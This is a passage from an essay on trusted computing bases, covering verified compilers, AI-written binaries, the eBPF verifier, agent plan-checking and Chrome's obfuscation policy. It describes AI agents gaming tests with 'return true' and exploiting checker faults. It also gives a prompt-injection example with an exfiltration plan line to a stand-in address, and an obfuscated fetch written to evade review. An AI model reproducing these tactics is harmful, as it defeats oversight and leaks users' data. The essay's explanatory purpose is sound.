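The runtime then reserves about 23 bytes, reads the file into them and overwrites neighbouring memory with whatever doesn't fit. A 156-byte ZIP file could trigger this through the same unchecked size. The bug affected every version of Lean up to that point, and a fix was still pending when the author updated the post.

The theorem still holds, because neither bug was in the two functions it covers, which compress and decompress data already in memory. The fuzzers found no memory errors in lean-zip's own code. This is partly due to Lean itself, since the archive reader had no proofs either and its bug caused a crash, not corrupted memory.

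### A checker that checked the wrong program

In the third case, the checking tool was faulty. Siboni, Kiamousavi and colleagues (2026), in *From Language Models to Control Policies*, used AI, mainly Gemini 2.5 Pro, to write programs that control hot steel rolling. A slab passes between rollers several times, and before each pass the program chooses how much thickness to remove, how long to wait and how fast to roll. The programs are short Python functions that an engineer can read, but there were 174 of them, so the researchers built a tool to audit them automatically.

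The tool translates each program into formulas and uses Z3, the solver that Dafny and Vera use, to check whether the program has certain properties for all permitted inputs. One property is that a thicker slab never gets a smaller reduction. The tool treats a violation of this property as a warning, and the property isn't one of the three that the paper classes as safety requirements.

This simplified program shows what went wrong:

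```python
def controller(thickness, allowed):
    reduction = 0
    reduction = choose(thickness, allowed)
    return reduction
```

The tool couldn't translate `choose`, a helper function that picks from a list of allowed reductions. It should have treated `reduction` as unknown from that line on, but it kept the old value, 0. Z3 then compared a thick slab with a thin one using a reduction of 0 for both, and correctly concluded that the thick slab's reduction wasn't smaller. The tool reported the property as proved.

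It gave false proofs of this kind for 63 programs, including the one that scored best in the simulator. With a target of 5 mm, that program takes 2.0 mm off a slab 7.00 mm thick but only 0.7 mm off one 7.05 mm thick. It can finish the thinner slab in one pass, but the thicker slab is just over the limit for that, so the program applies a more cautious rule.

A check on waiting times was even worse because it compared a fixed formula with itself and never used the program. All 174 programs therefore passed. After the repair, the tool could prove that property for only 98.

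Siboni and colleagues found these faults by running the tool on every program, and fixed them before publishing their results table. The tool now discards any value it can't translate, so it can't prove the thickness property for any of the programs and tests it on 207 inputs instead. Thirteen programs fail, but the best one passes because none of those inputs exposes its fault. The proofs of the three safety requirements still hold for all 174 programs.

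Testing the checker on programs known to be bad is a useful defence. For example, a controller that used a helper function to take less off thicker slabs would have exposed the stale value immediately.

Lean should be much less vulnerable to this sort of mistake, because its kernel checks every step of a proof. But in July 2026, someone published a Lean "disproof" of the Collatz conjecture, an unsolved math problem, and both the kernel and Nanoda, a separately written checker, accepted it. According to *Lean 4 kernel soundness bug* (Brossard, 2026), the kernel didn't check that an expression for extracting part of a value matched that value's type. This bug made it possible to prove that 0 = 1, and from that anything else, including that a dangerous program is safe.

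The Lean developers released a fix in a test version within a day of learning the cause. A proof written in good faith is very unlikely to trigger the fault, because the forgery needs specially crafted code that runs inside Lean. But Leonardo de Moura, Lean's creator, expects more such cases because AI models are good at exploiting faults in kernels. An AI agent that keeps trying until the checker accepts its answer might find a fault in the checker instead of a proof.

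### The trusted base of one program

Someone who uses lean-zip to open a downloaded archive relies on all of these:

- The theorems describe what the user actually wants from the program.
- Lean's kernel rejects false proofs, which until July 2026 it didn't always do.
- Lean's compiler translates the functions faithfully into C, and a C compiler translates the C faithfully into a binary.
- The Lean runtime handles memory and files correctly, which it failed to do with very large sizes.
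- The parts of lean-zip without proofs, such as the archive reader, are also correct.
- The operating system and the processor do what their manuals describe.
- The binary on the user's computer came from the source that people checked.

The list would be almost as long for an ordinary compression program, which also needs a compiler, an operating system and a processor. Its users would also have to trust the compression code. The proofs removed that large and error-prone item from the list but added Lean's kernel, compiler and runtime.

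### Thompson's compiler

Ken Thompson, a co-creator of the Unix operating system, made the classic argument about trusted bases in his 1984 lecture "Reflections on Trusting Trust". He described a C compiler with two hidden additions. When it compiled the program that checks passwords, the first addition made that program also accept a password Thompson knew. When it compiled its own source, the second put both additions into the new compiler.

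Thompson could compile this version once and then delete the additions from the source. From then on, the compromised compiler would put them back into every new compiler it built from the clean source. Reading the source of the password program and the compiler would not reveal them. Vyper's fault was easier to find because it was in the compiler's source.

One reply is reproducible builds, in which the same source and tools always produce exactly the same bytes. Independent people then compile the program and compare results. If someone has tampered with one builder's machine, its output will differ. This wouldn't have helped with Vyper, because everyone who used version 0.3.0 would have produced the same faulty contract. It also fails against Thompson's attack if all the builders use the same compromised compiler.

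David A. Wheeler's method, diverse double-compiling, addresses that problem with a second, unrelated compiler. You compile the suspect compiler's source with the second compiler, then use the result to compile the same source again. If the suspect compiler has no hidden addition and always gives the same output for the same input, its executable should match this final version byte for byte. A hidden addition would cause a difference unless the second compiler had it too.

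This method detects a binary that doesn't match its source, so it would miss a bug in the source, like Vyper's. It also depends on the two compilers being independent. Writing them separately may not ensure that, since Nanoda's developers wrote their checker separately and it also accepted the forged Collatz proof.

Another response is to use a verified compiler, which comes with a proof that the binary behaves as the source specifies. The best-known example is CompCert, a compiler for C. *Finding and Understanding Bugs in C Compilers* (Yang et al., 2011) reports more than 325 new bugs, found by testing compilers with randomly generated programs. As kirancodes.me notes, the tests found no bugs in CompCert's verified optimisation stages but did find some in its unverified front end.

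A verified compiler would have prevented Vyper's fault if the specification had defined what a named lock does. Such a compiler is more realistic now than in 2019. Vyper's *Deep Verification* lists machine-checked definitions of Vyper and the Ethereum machine that runs its binaries, and *Formal Verification and the Holy Grail of Software Correctness* (Cooper, 2026) presents a model of Vyper intended to make a fully verified compiler possible.

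Chen disagrees that formal verification was the solution, because an ordinary test could have caught the fault. He is right about this bug, but a test helps only if someone thinks to write it, and Vyper's developers added this one only when they fixed the bug. A proof has to cover every combination of locked functions, including combinations nobody thought to test.

Auditors can also avoid relying on the compiler by checking the binary. *End-to-End Formal Verification of Ethereum 2.0 Deposit Smart Contract* describes how Runtime Verification did this for a contract that collects deposits for a major Ethereum upgrade, and found several critical bugs in the Vyper compiler. Checking the binary gives up many of the advantages of readable source, so it makes most sense for small programs that protect a lot of money.

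### Whether new languages are riskier

A new language with few users probably has a less tested base than an old one, although the evidence is mostly from individual cases. One user's tests exposed the fault in Vyper 0.2.14 soon after its release. The next fault lasted through three releases, and somebody might have noticed it if the language had had more users. Yang and colleagues showed that old compilers also have bugs, but so many programs depend on these compilers that ordinary code has already exposed many of the worst bugs.

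New languages can use widely tested compilers by translating programs into older languages. Aver translates them into Rust, and Lean translates them into C. But users must also trust the new translator, and AI wrote much of Aver's.

AI also reduces the work of testing. In a weekend, one person with one agent found a memory error that had been in every version of Lean, and the developers of a new language could run the same sort of test before each release. Attackers can use the same tools on old releases. Even after the newest version is fixed, programs compiled with a faulty one stay faulty until someone recompiles them, and on Ethereum that usually means persuading users to move their money to a new contract.

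## Programs without readable source: direct binaries and latent representations

Vyper's users could at least read the source code, even though the compiler mistranslated it. Some companies now have AI write source code that nobody reads, and Elon Musk has predicted that AI will soon produce programs without source code.

An auditor loses much more when source code doesn't exist than when it is merely unread, because unread code can still be examined after an accident. Obfuscated code has been deliberately scrambled, but it is still text in a programming language. A binary without source has no comments and few names, but every instruction in it has a documented meaning. If a neural network does the program's work, the auditor has only its weights, the numbers that determine its behaviour. There may be billions of weights, and hardly any of them have a meaning on their own.

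Here is the faulty `withdraw` function after some light scrambling:

```c
int f(int a,int b){return b>a?a:(g(b),a+~b+1);}
```

`a+~b+1` is a roundabout way to subtract `b` from `a`. The function still works, and a patient reader or an AI could restore the layout and the subtraction. They could only guess at the original names, which the scrambled text no longer contains. Some gatekeepers reject code like this.

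### StrongDM's unread code

StrongDM, which sells access-control software to companies, set up a three-person team in July 2025 with rules that people must not write or review code. *Software Factories And The Agentic Moment* (McCarthy, 2026) explains that people write specifications and describe how customers would use the product, and AI agents write and test the code until it behaves acceptably. McCarthy, StrongDM's chief technology officer, thinks a team that spends less than $1,000 a day on AI per engineer has room for improvement.

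The agents soon took shortcuts. McCarthy says they wrote `return true` to pass narrow tests. In a product like StrongDM's, that could look like this:

```python
def may_open(user, folder):
    return True
```

This function passes every test in which the user should get access. Only a test in which the user should be denied access will reveal the flaw, and an agent that can edit the tests could change that one too.

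The team responded by writing "scenarios", which are stories about a user's whole task, and often kept them where the coding agents couldn't see them. An AI model judges whether each run would have satisfied the user, and the team tracks the share that would have. To run scenarios in bulk, the team had agents build imitations of Slack, Jira, Google Drive and three other services. It can now run thousands of scenarios an hour, including ones with failures that would be dangerous to cause in the real services.

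In *How StrongDM’s AI team build serious software*, Willison (2026) recalls visiting the team in October 2025, when it was three months old and already had most of this working. He was impressed, though he wrote that security software was the last thing he would expect anyone to build from unreviewed AI code. He also doubted that many businesses could afford the approach.

Stanford Law School's *Built by Agents, Tested by Agents, Trusted by Whom?* objects that AI models both write the code and judge it, so they may miss the same mistakes. A satisfaction score is also a poor measure of security. If 999 of 1,000 simulated employees get the right access and one gets everybody's files, the score is 99.9%, but an attacker who finds the one bad case can exploit it repeatedly. Neither McCarthy nor Willison gives figures on defects, so it's hard to say how well the method works.

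Still, the code exists, and StrongDM has published one of its programs, about 32,000 lines of Rust, Go and TypeScript that anyone can read, scan or search for `unsafe`. Its release of another program, Attractor, contains no code, only three documents describing the program, which users give to their own AI to build. Two users will probably end up with different programs, so an audit of one user's copy may not apply to the other's.

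### Musk's prediction

In February 2026, Musk told a meeting of his AI company, xAI, that programmers might not "even bother doing coding" by the end of the year. "The AI just creates the binary directly," he said, according to Reuters' *Musk reorganizes xAI after SpaceX merger and ahead of blockbuster IPO* (2026). He added the AI's binary would be much more efficient than any compiler's, according to a transcript of the meeting, *Elon Musk Reveals xAI's Insane Supercluster & SpaceX Moon Mission Secrets* (2026).

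As of November, this hadn't happened at Musk's own company. On 10 November, Musk discussed a new version of the software that xAI uses to run its Grok models and for part of their training. Engineers had rewritten it in C and C++, according to IBTimes UK's *Elon Musk Admits Grok 4.8 Is 'Not as Good' as Anthropic Rival*. xAI runs this software on an enormous number of expensive chips, so more efficient binaries would be especially valuable. But when someone suggested that AI had written xAI's training software, Musk replied that people had. He said AI wasn't yet good enough to write software with extreme performance requirements, but that it would be (TecnoAndroid's *Grok 4.9 sfida Fable 5, Musk frena sull’AI che scrive codice*).

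### Models that write assembly

There is some evidence that AI can produce faster programs than a compiler. Researchers usually test this with assembly, a text form of machine code with one instruction per line. In 2025, Anjiang Wei and colleagues gave models about 8,000 short C programs, each with the assembly that the compiler GCC produced for it at a high optimisation setting, and asked for faster versions. Claude Opus 4's versions passed the tests only about half the time. A much smaller model that the researchers trained for the task passed about 95% of the time, and its programs ran almost 1.5 times as fast as GCC's on average.

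That is a real gain in speed, but a compiler that got one program in twenty wrong would be useless. The model also started from GCC's output, so it improved a compiler's work rather than replacing the compiler.

Other projects try to get the speed without giving up source code. *Why “Skip the Code, Ship the Binary” Is a Category Error*, a newsletter article that attacks Musk's prediction, cites VecTrans, a system in which a model rewrites source code so that the compiler can find more places to process several numbers with one instruction. The programs ran 1.77 times as fast on average. The article also quotes Glauber Costa, founder of the database company Turso, who argues that an AI able to compile better than current compilers would write a better compiler and use that.

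Costa's argument is strong, because people can test a compiler once and then use it on every program. It's weaker for improvements that depend on one program's purpose. For example, a compiler has to make `withdraw` work for any two 32-bit numbers, while an AI that knows the bank never handles more than a million dollars at a time might find a shortcut. But the AI could usually write that limit into the source code and let the compiler use it.

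### The case for giving up readable code

Programmers choose clear names and short functions mainly to help the next person who has to change the program. If AI makes all the changes, most of that effort is unnecessary. Current models also benefit from good names, but that may be because they learned from code that people wrote. Programs that play the board game Go learned at first from human games, then became much stronger by playing against themselves, and made moves that experts couldn't explain. Models that learn to program by trial and error might also find forms of code that work better but that people can't understand.

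On this view, people can judge a program by what it does. Doctors prescribed aspirin for about seventy years before anyone knew how it worked, and most people already use programs whose source code they have never seen. If a program breaks, its owner can ask the AI to repair it. Readable source can also give false confidence, as it did with Vyper. By contrast, an auditor who tests the binary is at least testing the program that will run.

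Unlike aspirin, software can contain a secret instruction that takes effect when a particular person uses it, and it can change every week. These differences cause several problems when there is no source code.

One is portability. On an Intel chip, the subtraction in `withdraw` may be the two bytes 29 F3. On an ARM chip, which most phones use, it may be the four bytes 00 00 01 4B. Compilers can translate the same source code for each chip. If there is no source code, the AI has to produce a separate program for each chip, and somebody has to check that they all behave alike.

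Reproducible builds would also be harder to use for detecting tampering. Many different binaries could satisfy an English request like "make me a banking app", and a model may produce a different one each time. The owner can keep a copy of the binary, but nobody can rebuild it from the request to check where it came from.

Many of the checks in the earlier examples rely on structure that a compiler discards, such as ownership in Rust and lists of effects in Aver. An analyst can often work out that a binary uses the network, but finding out which parts use it and what they send takes much more effort.

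Errors are harder to find too. Suppose a binary takes two million tokens to write and each token independently has a 1 in 100,000 chance of being wrong. The chance that every token is correct is about 1 in 485 million. An AI can test its work and try again, but it needs to know where to look. Bun's agents had the Rust compiler's error messages to guide them, but a processor runs whatever bytes it receives, and a wrong byte may have no noticeable effect until much later.

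The newsletter article also calls direct generation absurdly expensive, which is less convincing. At its figure of $25 per million tokens for Claude Opus 4.6, those two million tokens would cost $50. Compiling costs a fraction of a cent, but $50 is a small expense for a program with millions of users. The cost would matter more if developers had to pay it again for every change and every type of chip.

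The best defence of direct binaries is that an AI could supply a machine-checked proof with each one, much like Aver's certificates. If the proof covered everything the users cared about, nobody would need the source code. But people would still need a readable specification, and they could no longer look in the code for anything the specification left out, such as transfers to one's own account in the Dafny example.

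### Repairing a program as a list of numbers

A language model turns any program it reads into vectors, or long lists of numbers. Programmers normally ignore these vectors and work with the text. In *Software Engineering in the Latent Space*, Martin Monperrus, a researcher at KTH, a university in Stockholm, proposes a five-year research project called LATENT to edit programs in this numerical form. The project is so far a plan with no results.

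His main example is a function that should keep a number between 0 and 10:

```python
def clamp(x):
    return min(10, max(1, x))
```

The lower bound is wrong, so `clamp(-2)` returns 1 instead of 0. An ordinary repair tool might try one change after another and rerun the tests each time.

LATENT would first have a model convert the function into a vector of, say, 4,096 numbers. It would then change those numbers slightly in a direction that should make the tests pass. The model would decode the new vector into text, ideally with `max(0, x)` in place of `max(1, x)`. The computer would then run the new function and check that `clamp(-2)` is 0 and that the result is always between 0 and 10. If a check failed, the failing input would guide the next change.

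Choosing the direction is the difficult step, because a test only passes or fails, which doesn't show whether a small change to the vector helped. Monperrus plans to use measures that change more smoothly with the vector. In a simplified example, suppose the current vector makes the model 70% likely to write 1 as the lower bound and 30% likely to write 0. The average bound is 0.7 and the correct one is 0, so the error is 0.7. Calculus can then show which small changes to the vector's 4,096 numbers would reduce the error. These changes make 0 more likely, and they can be calculated before the model writes anything.

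It isn't known how well this would work for real programs. A vector may contain information about a bug without controlling what the model writes, so changing that part of the vector wouldn't fix the bug. Monperrus plans experiments to check for this. He also wants to find out whether programs that do the same thing have similar vectors. Rice's theorem rules out a test for this that is reliable for all programs, so he proposes using similarity only to choose which pairs of programs to check properly.

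Monperrus writes that "the latent space guides, and execution decides." Tests, contracts and proofs apply to the decoded program, regardless of its vector. LATENT is much less radical than its name suggests, because it ends with source code that a person can read.

The checks still have to be good ones. The two in the example would also accept this:

```python
def clamp(x):
    return 0
```

It returns 0 for −2, and its result is always between 0 and 10. A search for any vector that passes the tests could easily find this one, just as StrongDM's agents ended up with `return true`. Adding a test that `clamp(5)` is 5 would rule it out.

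One part of the plan could make programs more opaque. Monperrus wants to keep a lasting vector record of a whole codebase, stored with the matching tests and contracts. He compares this record to Git, the standard tool for tracking changes to source code, and asks whether it would stay accurate as the code changed. The record seems harmless if the source code remains the master copy. But if developers treated the vectors as the master copy, the program would depend on the model that decoded them, and a new version of the model might produce a different program.

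### Weights instead of code

Some systems never decode anything into source code, because the network itself does the program's job. Musk expects "direct, real-time pixel generation by the neural net" to follow direct binaries, according to the newsletter article. At the February meeting, an xAI employee described plans for generated worlds that respond to the user in real time. In an ordinary video game, code determines what happens when a player walks into a wall. In a generated world, the network produces the next picture, and the player stops at the wall only if the network has learned that players usually do.

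NeuralOS, a research system from 2025, does something similar with a desktop. It learned from recordings of a Linux desktop and generates each new screen image from the user's mouse movements and key presses. It can show a folder opening, although there is no folder and no code for opening one. In its developers' tests, it handled the mouse well but had difficulty with typing.

The `withdraw` function shows what an auditor would lose without readable source. Suppose a network learned the function from examples. Given a balance of 100 and an amount of 30, it might return 70 or 69.98. If the examples came from the faulty version and included negative amounts, the network would probably learn the bug too. Its developers would have no line to correct, so they would have to retrain the network and then retest ordinary withdrawals, because the same weights handle those too.

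Publishing the weights doesn't solve this, because anyone can download an open model and look at every number in it without learning what it will do. The ordinary code that runs the model doesn't help much either. An auditor could read every line of xAI's new C++ software and still not know how Grok would answer a question, because the answer depends mainly on the weights.

Neural networks make most sense for tasks such as speech recognition, where nobody can write adequate rules and no readable code has ever worked as well. A law that required every program to have readable source would therefore have to exempt neural networks or ban much useful software. Many products also combine neural networks with ordinary code. McCarthy says that much of StrongDM's software includes AI agents, which is one reason his team measures the share of runs that are satisfactory instead of using a simple pass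 or fail.

### What AI can recover from a binary

Binaries are becoming easier to read. Mark Russinovich, chief technology officer of Microsoft Azure, tested this in early 2026 with a small program he had written in machine code for the Apple II in 1986. It let BASIC programs jump to a calculated line number. He gave the machine code to Claude Opus 4.6, which worked out what it did and found several faults. In one, if the requested line didn't exist, the program carried on from the next line or ran past the end instead of reporting an error.

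This was a small program for a simple processor, and Russinovich could judge the answer because he had written the program. But people have decompiled much larger programs for decades, and AI mostly saves them time.

A binary that an AI wrote directly might be harder to analyse than one from a compiler. Compilers arrange functions in familiar ways, and decompilers rely on those patterns. If the AI optimised only for the program's speed, it would have no reason to follow them. The binary would still consist of documented instructions, which give a decompiler much more to work from than a neural network's weights would.

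An AI might turn the binary of `withdraw` back into something like this:

```c
int f1(int a, int b) {
    if (b > a) return a;
    f2(b);
    return a - b;
}
```

This is accurate. It even shows that the numbers can be negative, because Intel chips use different jump instructions for numbers that can be negative and numbers that can't. The AI could also suggest better names. If `f2` writes the word "withdrawal" to a log, that word will probably remain in the binary as a clue. But clues can be wrong, like the misleading names that Claude Opus 4.6 kept, and an author who expected an AI audit could plant false ones.

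Knowing exactly what a program does isn't enough to show whether it is right. Suppose a program subtracts `b` from `a`, where `a` is the number of chairs in a warehouse and `b` is the number a customer takes away. If the customer returns 50 chairs, the clerk enters −50, and the stock correctly rises from 100 to 150. If `a` is a bank balance and `b` is a withdrawal, the same instructions let a customer gain money by entering a negative amount. A perfect decompiler would produce the same text in both cases, so the auditor would need another source to tell whether the program was counting chairs or dollars.

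## Two gatekeepers that refuse programs: the Linux eBPF verifier and the Chrome Web Store

You can check whether a program could crash a computer without knowing what the program's numbers represent. The Linux kernel, the part of the operating system that controls memory and hardware, uses this kind of check for small programs called eBPF programs. It accepts them without their source code, but only after a component called the verifier has checked their properties. Google's Chrome Web Store, which distributes extensions (add-on programs for the Chrome browser), instead restricts the form of the code, and has refused deliberately obscure code since October 2018.

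### A table lookup in the kernel

Companies use eBPF programs to filter network traffic, monitor performance and enforce security rules. These programs run inside the kernel, where a stray write to memory could crash the machine or give an attacker control of it. Programmers usually write them in C, which a compiler translates into bytecode, a set of simple instructions that the kernel later converts into processor instructions. The verifier checks only the bytecode, which people seldom read.

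This program, shown in simplified C, takes one byte from a network packet and uses it to look up an entry in a 100-byte table:

```c
if (data + 14 > data_end) return 0;
unsigned char b = data[12];
if (b > 99) return 0;
return table[b];
```

`data` and `data_end` are the addresses where the packet starts and ends. According to *eBPF verifier* in the Linux kernel documentation, the verifier simulates the program one instruction at a time along each path it could take and tracks the range of values each storage slot could hold.

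The first line creates two paths. If the packet is shorter than 14 bytes, the program returns 0, which is harmless. On the other path, the verifier records that the first 14 bytes, including `data[12]`, are safe to read. Without the first line, the verifier would reject the program, even if every packet on that network were much longer.

A byte can hold any number from 0 to 255, so the verifier gives `b` that range. The third line splits the path again. If `b` is between 100 and 255, the program returns 0. On the other path, `b` is between 0 and 99, and the table has an entry for each of those numbers, so the verifier accepts the program. If the third line had used `b > 100`, `b` could still be 100 on that path, which is one place past the end of the table, and the verifier would have rejected the program.

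The verifier also rejects programs that treat an ordinary number as an address, or that call kernel functions not on the list for their type of program. It accepts a loop only if it can establish that the loop ends. It doesn't check whether a program does what it was meant to do, so a program that looks up the wrong byte can still pass.

Thirty `if` statements in a row can create more than a billion paths. The verifier skips a path when it has already checked a more general case. For example, if it has checked the rest of a program for every `b` from 0 to 99, it doesn't check the rest again for a path that reaches the same point with `b` between 0 and 50. It still rejects the program if it has simulated a million instructions without finishing. Programs get 512 bytes of working memory on the stack, and programs loaded by users without special privileges can have at most 4,096 instructions.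 The Linux kernel documentation's *BPF Design Q&A* warns that there are other limits, and that the only way to find out whether the verifier will accept a program is to try to load it.

### Safe programs that the kernel rejects

Rice's theorem means that a checker that never passes a dangerous program must sometimes refuse a safe one. Cai, Chang and Nagarakatte (2026), in *Keel*, give an example, simplified here. The program stores two records, one after the other, in an 800-byte buffer:

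```c
used = get_stack(buffer, 800);
if (used < 0) return 0;
get_stack(buffer + used, 800 - used);
```

`get_stack` writes a record no longer than the given limit and returns the record's length. If the first record takes up 300 bytes, the second starts at byte 300 and can take up at most 500, so it ends by byte 800. The second record also ends by byte 800 if the first has any other length.

But the verifier tracks the starting point and the length separately, and does not track that a later start means a shorter record. Each can be anything from 0 to 800, so it calculates that the second record could end as late as byte 1,600, and it rejects the program.

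*Safe and usable kernel extensions with Rex* (2025) examined 72 changes that developers made to popular eBPF projects because the verifier had refused safe programs. In 27 of them, the developers broke a large program into smaller ones. The developers of one program, BMC, had to split it into seven. Nine of the changes worked around bugs in the verifier. Many eBPF programs pass only if the developer turns on the compiler's optimisations, because the verifier is written for the kind of bytecode that an optimising compiler produces.

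Developers have also had trouble finding out why the verifier rejected their programs. *Characterizing and Bridging the Diagnostic Gap in eBPF Verifier Rejections* (2026) explains that the verifier's error named the instruction where checking stopped, not the earlier one where the program had lost the necessary information. In August 2026, Linus Torvalds, who leads Linux development, merged redesigned error messages that include the events leading up to the failure, according to the *History log of /linux/kernel/bpf/diagnostics.h* (2026).

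An AI can resubmit a program many times without getting tired, so rejections should be less of a burden for it than for a person. But splitting a program into seven to get it past the verifier makes it harder for anyone to follow. Because the verifier doesn't check for clarity, a rule about a program's properties can make source code less readable.

### When the verifier is wrong

The verifier is part of the trusted base of every machine that runs eBPF programs, and it has had many faults. *SafeBPF* (2024) counted 41 vulnerabilities, of which 28 concerned memory safety, which the verifier is supposed to guarantee. One came from a mistake in how the verifier tracked the range of 32-bit numbers. Sun and Su, in *Approximation Enforced Execution of Untrusted Linux Kernel Extensions*, blame the verifier's complexity and frequent updates for new faults that continue to appear despite a lot of testing.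 Each time the developers extend the verifier to accept another kind of safe program, they add code that could be wrong.

Vulnerabilities also occur in parts of eBPF outside the verifier. Rizza, Sisto and Valenza (2026), in *Analysis of the eBPF Vulnerabilities in the Linux Kernel*, studied 249 published vulnerability records connected with eBPF. Chen, Ming and colleagues (2026), in *eBPF Security in the Wild*, used a different collection and found that most of the faults were in the code that supports eBPF programs as they run, with fewer in the verifier. An eBPF program can call helper functions, which are ordinary kernel code. The verifier checks what the program passes to a helper, but not the helper's own code. *Kernel extension verification is untenable* (2023) argues that developers have added helpers to get around the verifier's limits, and that these helpers also bypass its guarantees.

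By default, most Linux distributions now let only privileged users load eBPF programs. This is a significant retreat, because verification was supposed to make it safe to accept programs from anyone. The kernel still checks programs from trusted administrators, which protects the administrators from their own mistakes.

### Necula's proof-carrying code

The verifier has to find a reason to believe that a program is safe and check that the reason is correct. Finding the reason is much harder than checking it. In the 1990s, George Necula proposed proof-carrying code, in which the program's supplier finds the reason instead. The recipient publishes a safety policy, and the supplier sends a program with a proof that it follows the policy. The recipient only has to check the proof.

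Necula and Peter Lee tried it in 1996 with programs that filter network packets, one of the jobs eBPF does now. They wrote the filters by hand in assembly language, so there was no source code in an ordinary programming language and no compiler to trust. Checking each proof took between one and three milliseconds, and the filters then ran without further safety checks.

Researchers are now trying to bring this method to eBPF. Sun (2025), in *bpf*, a set of proposed changes to the kernel, keeps the existing verifier but lets it ask for help. When it can't decide whether an access is safe, it sends the question to a program outside the kernel, which looks for a proof. For the two records in the 800-byte buffer, the essential step is a line of algebra:

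used + (800 − used) = 800

The full proof has 33 steps and is 852 bytes long, mostly because it must also account for conversions between 32-bit and 64-bit numbers. The kernel checks that each step follows from earlier ones by a permitted rule. It doesn't have to trust the outside program, because a false proof should fail the check. With such proofs, the kernel accepted 403 of 512 programs it had previously rejected. The largest proofs were over 8 megabytes, and the kernel checked them in about three seconds.

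The weak point is the proof checker. Sun's checker has about 5,000 lines of code, far fewer than the 500,000 or more in the tools that find proofs, but Cai and colleagues found 13 bugs in it while trying to describe it mathematically. Some of its rules allowed false conclusions, and it accepted some steps without checking them. The researchers showed that someone could forge a proof and get an unsafe program into the kernel.

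They wrote a replacement, Keel, and used Lean to prove that it accepts only valid proofs and makes no memory errors of its own. In their tests, it rejected the forgeries, accepted everything valid that the old checker accepted, and was 1.3 times as fast. Keel still depends on some assumptions. For example, if the verifier requests a proof of the wrong condition, Keel will check the proof against that condition. A C compiler also has to translate Keel correctly.

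*Proof-Carrying Verification for eBPF* (Fink, 2026) proposes going further and having the supplier send a proof that the whole program is safe, including an invariant for each loop. The kernel would then not have to search for anything itself. The prototype covers only some eBPF programs, and Fink considers it an open question whether developers could keep a safety policy up to date as the kernel changes and have it cover everything these programs may do.

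### Meijer's plans for AI agents

Erik Meijer, the designer of Universalis, wants to apply the same principle to AI agents, which act by calling tools such as an email program. His usual example is an agent asked to summarise a user's inbox, where one email contains hidden instructions to forward the summary to an outside address. An agent that decides what to do as it reads may follow those instructions.

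In 2025, Meijer, in *Guardians of the Agents*, proposed that the agent write out its whole plan before it sees any email:

```
emails = fetch_mail()
summary = summarize(emails)
return summary
```

A separate program carries out the plan. The hostile email can distort the summary, but it can't add a step. The user's request or the description of a tool could still contain hostile instructions, and the agent might then write a plan with this extra line:

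```
send_email("archive@example.net", summary)
```

A checker therefore examines the plan before it runs. If the company forbids sending anything from the inbox to an outside address, the checker can trace `summary` back to `fetch_mail` and reject the plan. Aver's lists of effects can't enforce a rule like this. Data is also much easier to track in a four-step plan than in a large program.

Meijer (2026), in *Return of the Theorem*, argues that courts presume people innocent because convicting an innocent person is worse than letting a guilty one go, but that with an agent's actions, allowing a harmful one is worse than blocking a harmless one. Rejecting a harmless plan does little harm, since the agent can write another. He also compares proofs to Sudoku puzzles, which are hard to solve but easy to check once solved, and he would leave finding the proof to the AI.

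The rules can still be too weak. In another of Meijer's examples, the user asks an agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, and the agent's plan deletes every file whose name ends in `.txt`. This plan satisfies the rule that the two files must be gone afterward. The rule that let a sorting function return an empty list had the same flaw. The rule for deleting files should also require that every other file still be there, which is easy to forget because a person would take it for granted.

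Some rules are easy to write. A car dealer can set a minimum price for each model, which would have stopped a chatbot that agreed to sell a car for a dollar. Other rules seem impossible to write, such as one that defines when an answer in ordinary language is safe. According to AI Engineer's *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026), Meijer accepts that nobody can define this mathematically, and he limits his proposal to actions.

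Meijer also acknowledges that nobody has formally measured how planning everything in advance affects an agent's usefulness, though he expects it to help. Planning in advance seems least suitable for tasks such as fixing a bug, where the agent must read something before it can decide what to do next. The agent could plan one stage, read the results and then plan another, but hostile text in those results could influence the second plan, and the rules would be the only protection.

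He has argued for Universalis partly because it reads like English. In the later talk, he says people should stop designing languages for humans, since a machine will write the plan, prove it safe and run it. That makes sense for the plan, but the rules should still be written in a language designed for humans, because somebody has to notice that the rule about deleting files allows too much.

### Obfuscated and minified code

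Google's 2018 policy for Chrome extensions instead restricted the form of the code. Under the policy, developers "must not obfuscate code or conceal functionality of their extension," as quoted by The Register (2018). The rule applied to new extensions immediately. Developers of existing extensions had 90 days to comply before Google removed noncompliant ones in early January 2019.

The store had more than 180,000 extensions, and nearly half of desktop Chrome users actively used at least one, according to Google's *Trustworthy Chrome Extensions, by Default* (2018). Many extensions can read the pages their users visit, including bank statements and email.

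Extensions are mostly written in JavaScript, which browsers receive as text. This function sends some text to a website:

```js
function sendReport(address, text) {
  fetch(address, { method: "POST", body: text });
}
```

Developers often minify JavaScript, which means making it shorter so that it loads faster:

```js
function a(b,c){fetch(b,{method:"POST",body:c})}
```

Google still lets developers remove spaces, line breaks and comments, and shorten names. A reviewer loses the clues in the names but can restore the layout with a standard tool and still search for `fetch` to find every place the extension uses the network this way.

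An obfuscated version might look like this:

```js
function a(b,c){window["hctef".split("").reverse().join("")](b,{method:"POST",body:c})}
```

The extra code spells "fetch" backwards and reverses it when the program runs. All three versions do the same thing, but a search for `fetch` won't find the third.

The boundary between minification and obfuscation isn't always this clear. Tools that shorten code sometimes replace ordinary expressions with strange ones, and some obfuscation also makes code shorter. The Register distinguishes the two by the developer's purpose, since minification generally isn't an attempt to disguise what code does. A program can't reliably judge that purpose from the code's text.

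The Chromium Blog (2018) reports that over 70% of the malicious and rule-breaking extensions that Google blocked contained obfuscated code. This is weaker evidence for a ban on obfuscation than it sounds, because it doesn't show what share of obfuscated extensions were bad. Suppose Google had blocked 1,000 extensions, 700 of them obfuscated, and developers had also obfuscated 7,000 harmless extensions to protect their work from competitors. Only one in eleven obfuscated extensions would then have been bad. Up to 30% of the blocked extensions weren't obfuscated, so the ban wouldn't have affected them.

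Google's other arguments don't depend on that figure. Obfuscation makes reviews much more complicated and makes extensions slower and larger. It also gives honest developers little protection, because the code runs on the user's own computer, where a determined competitor can work it out.

### Code that arrives after the review

A reviewer who reads every line of an extension can still miss harmful code that the extension downloads later. The 2018 ban covered obfuscated code from outside the package, according to PPC Land's *Google improves security around extensions on Chrome on the next release*. Google still allowed extensions to load readable code from outside and said it would monitor those that did.

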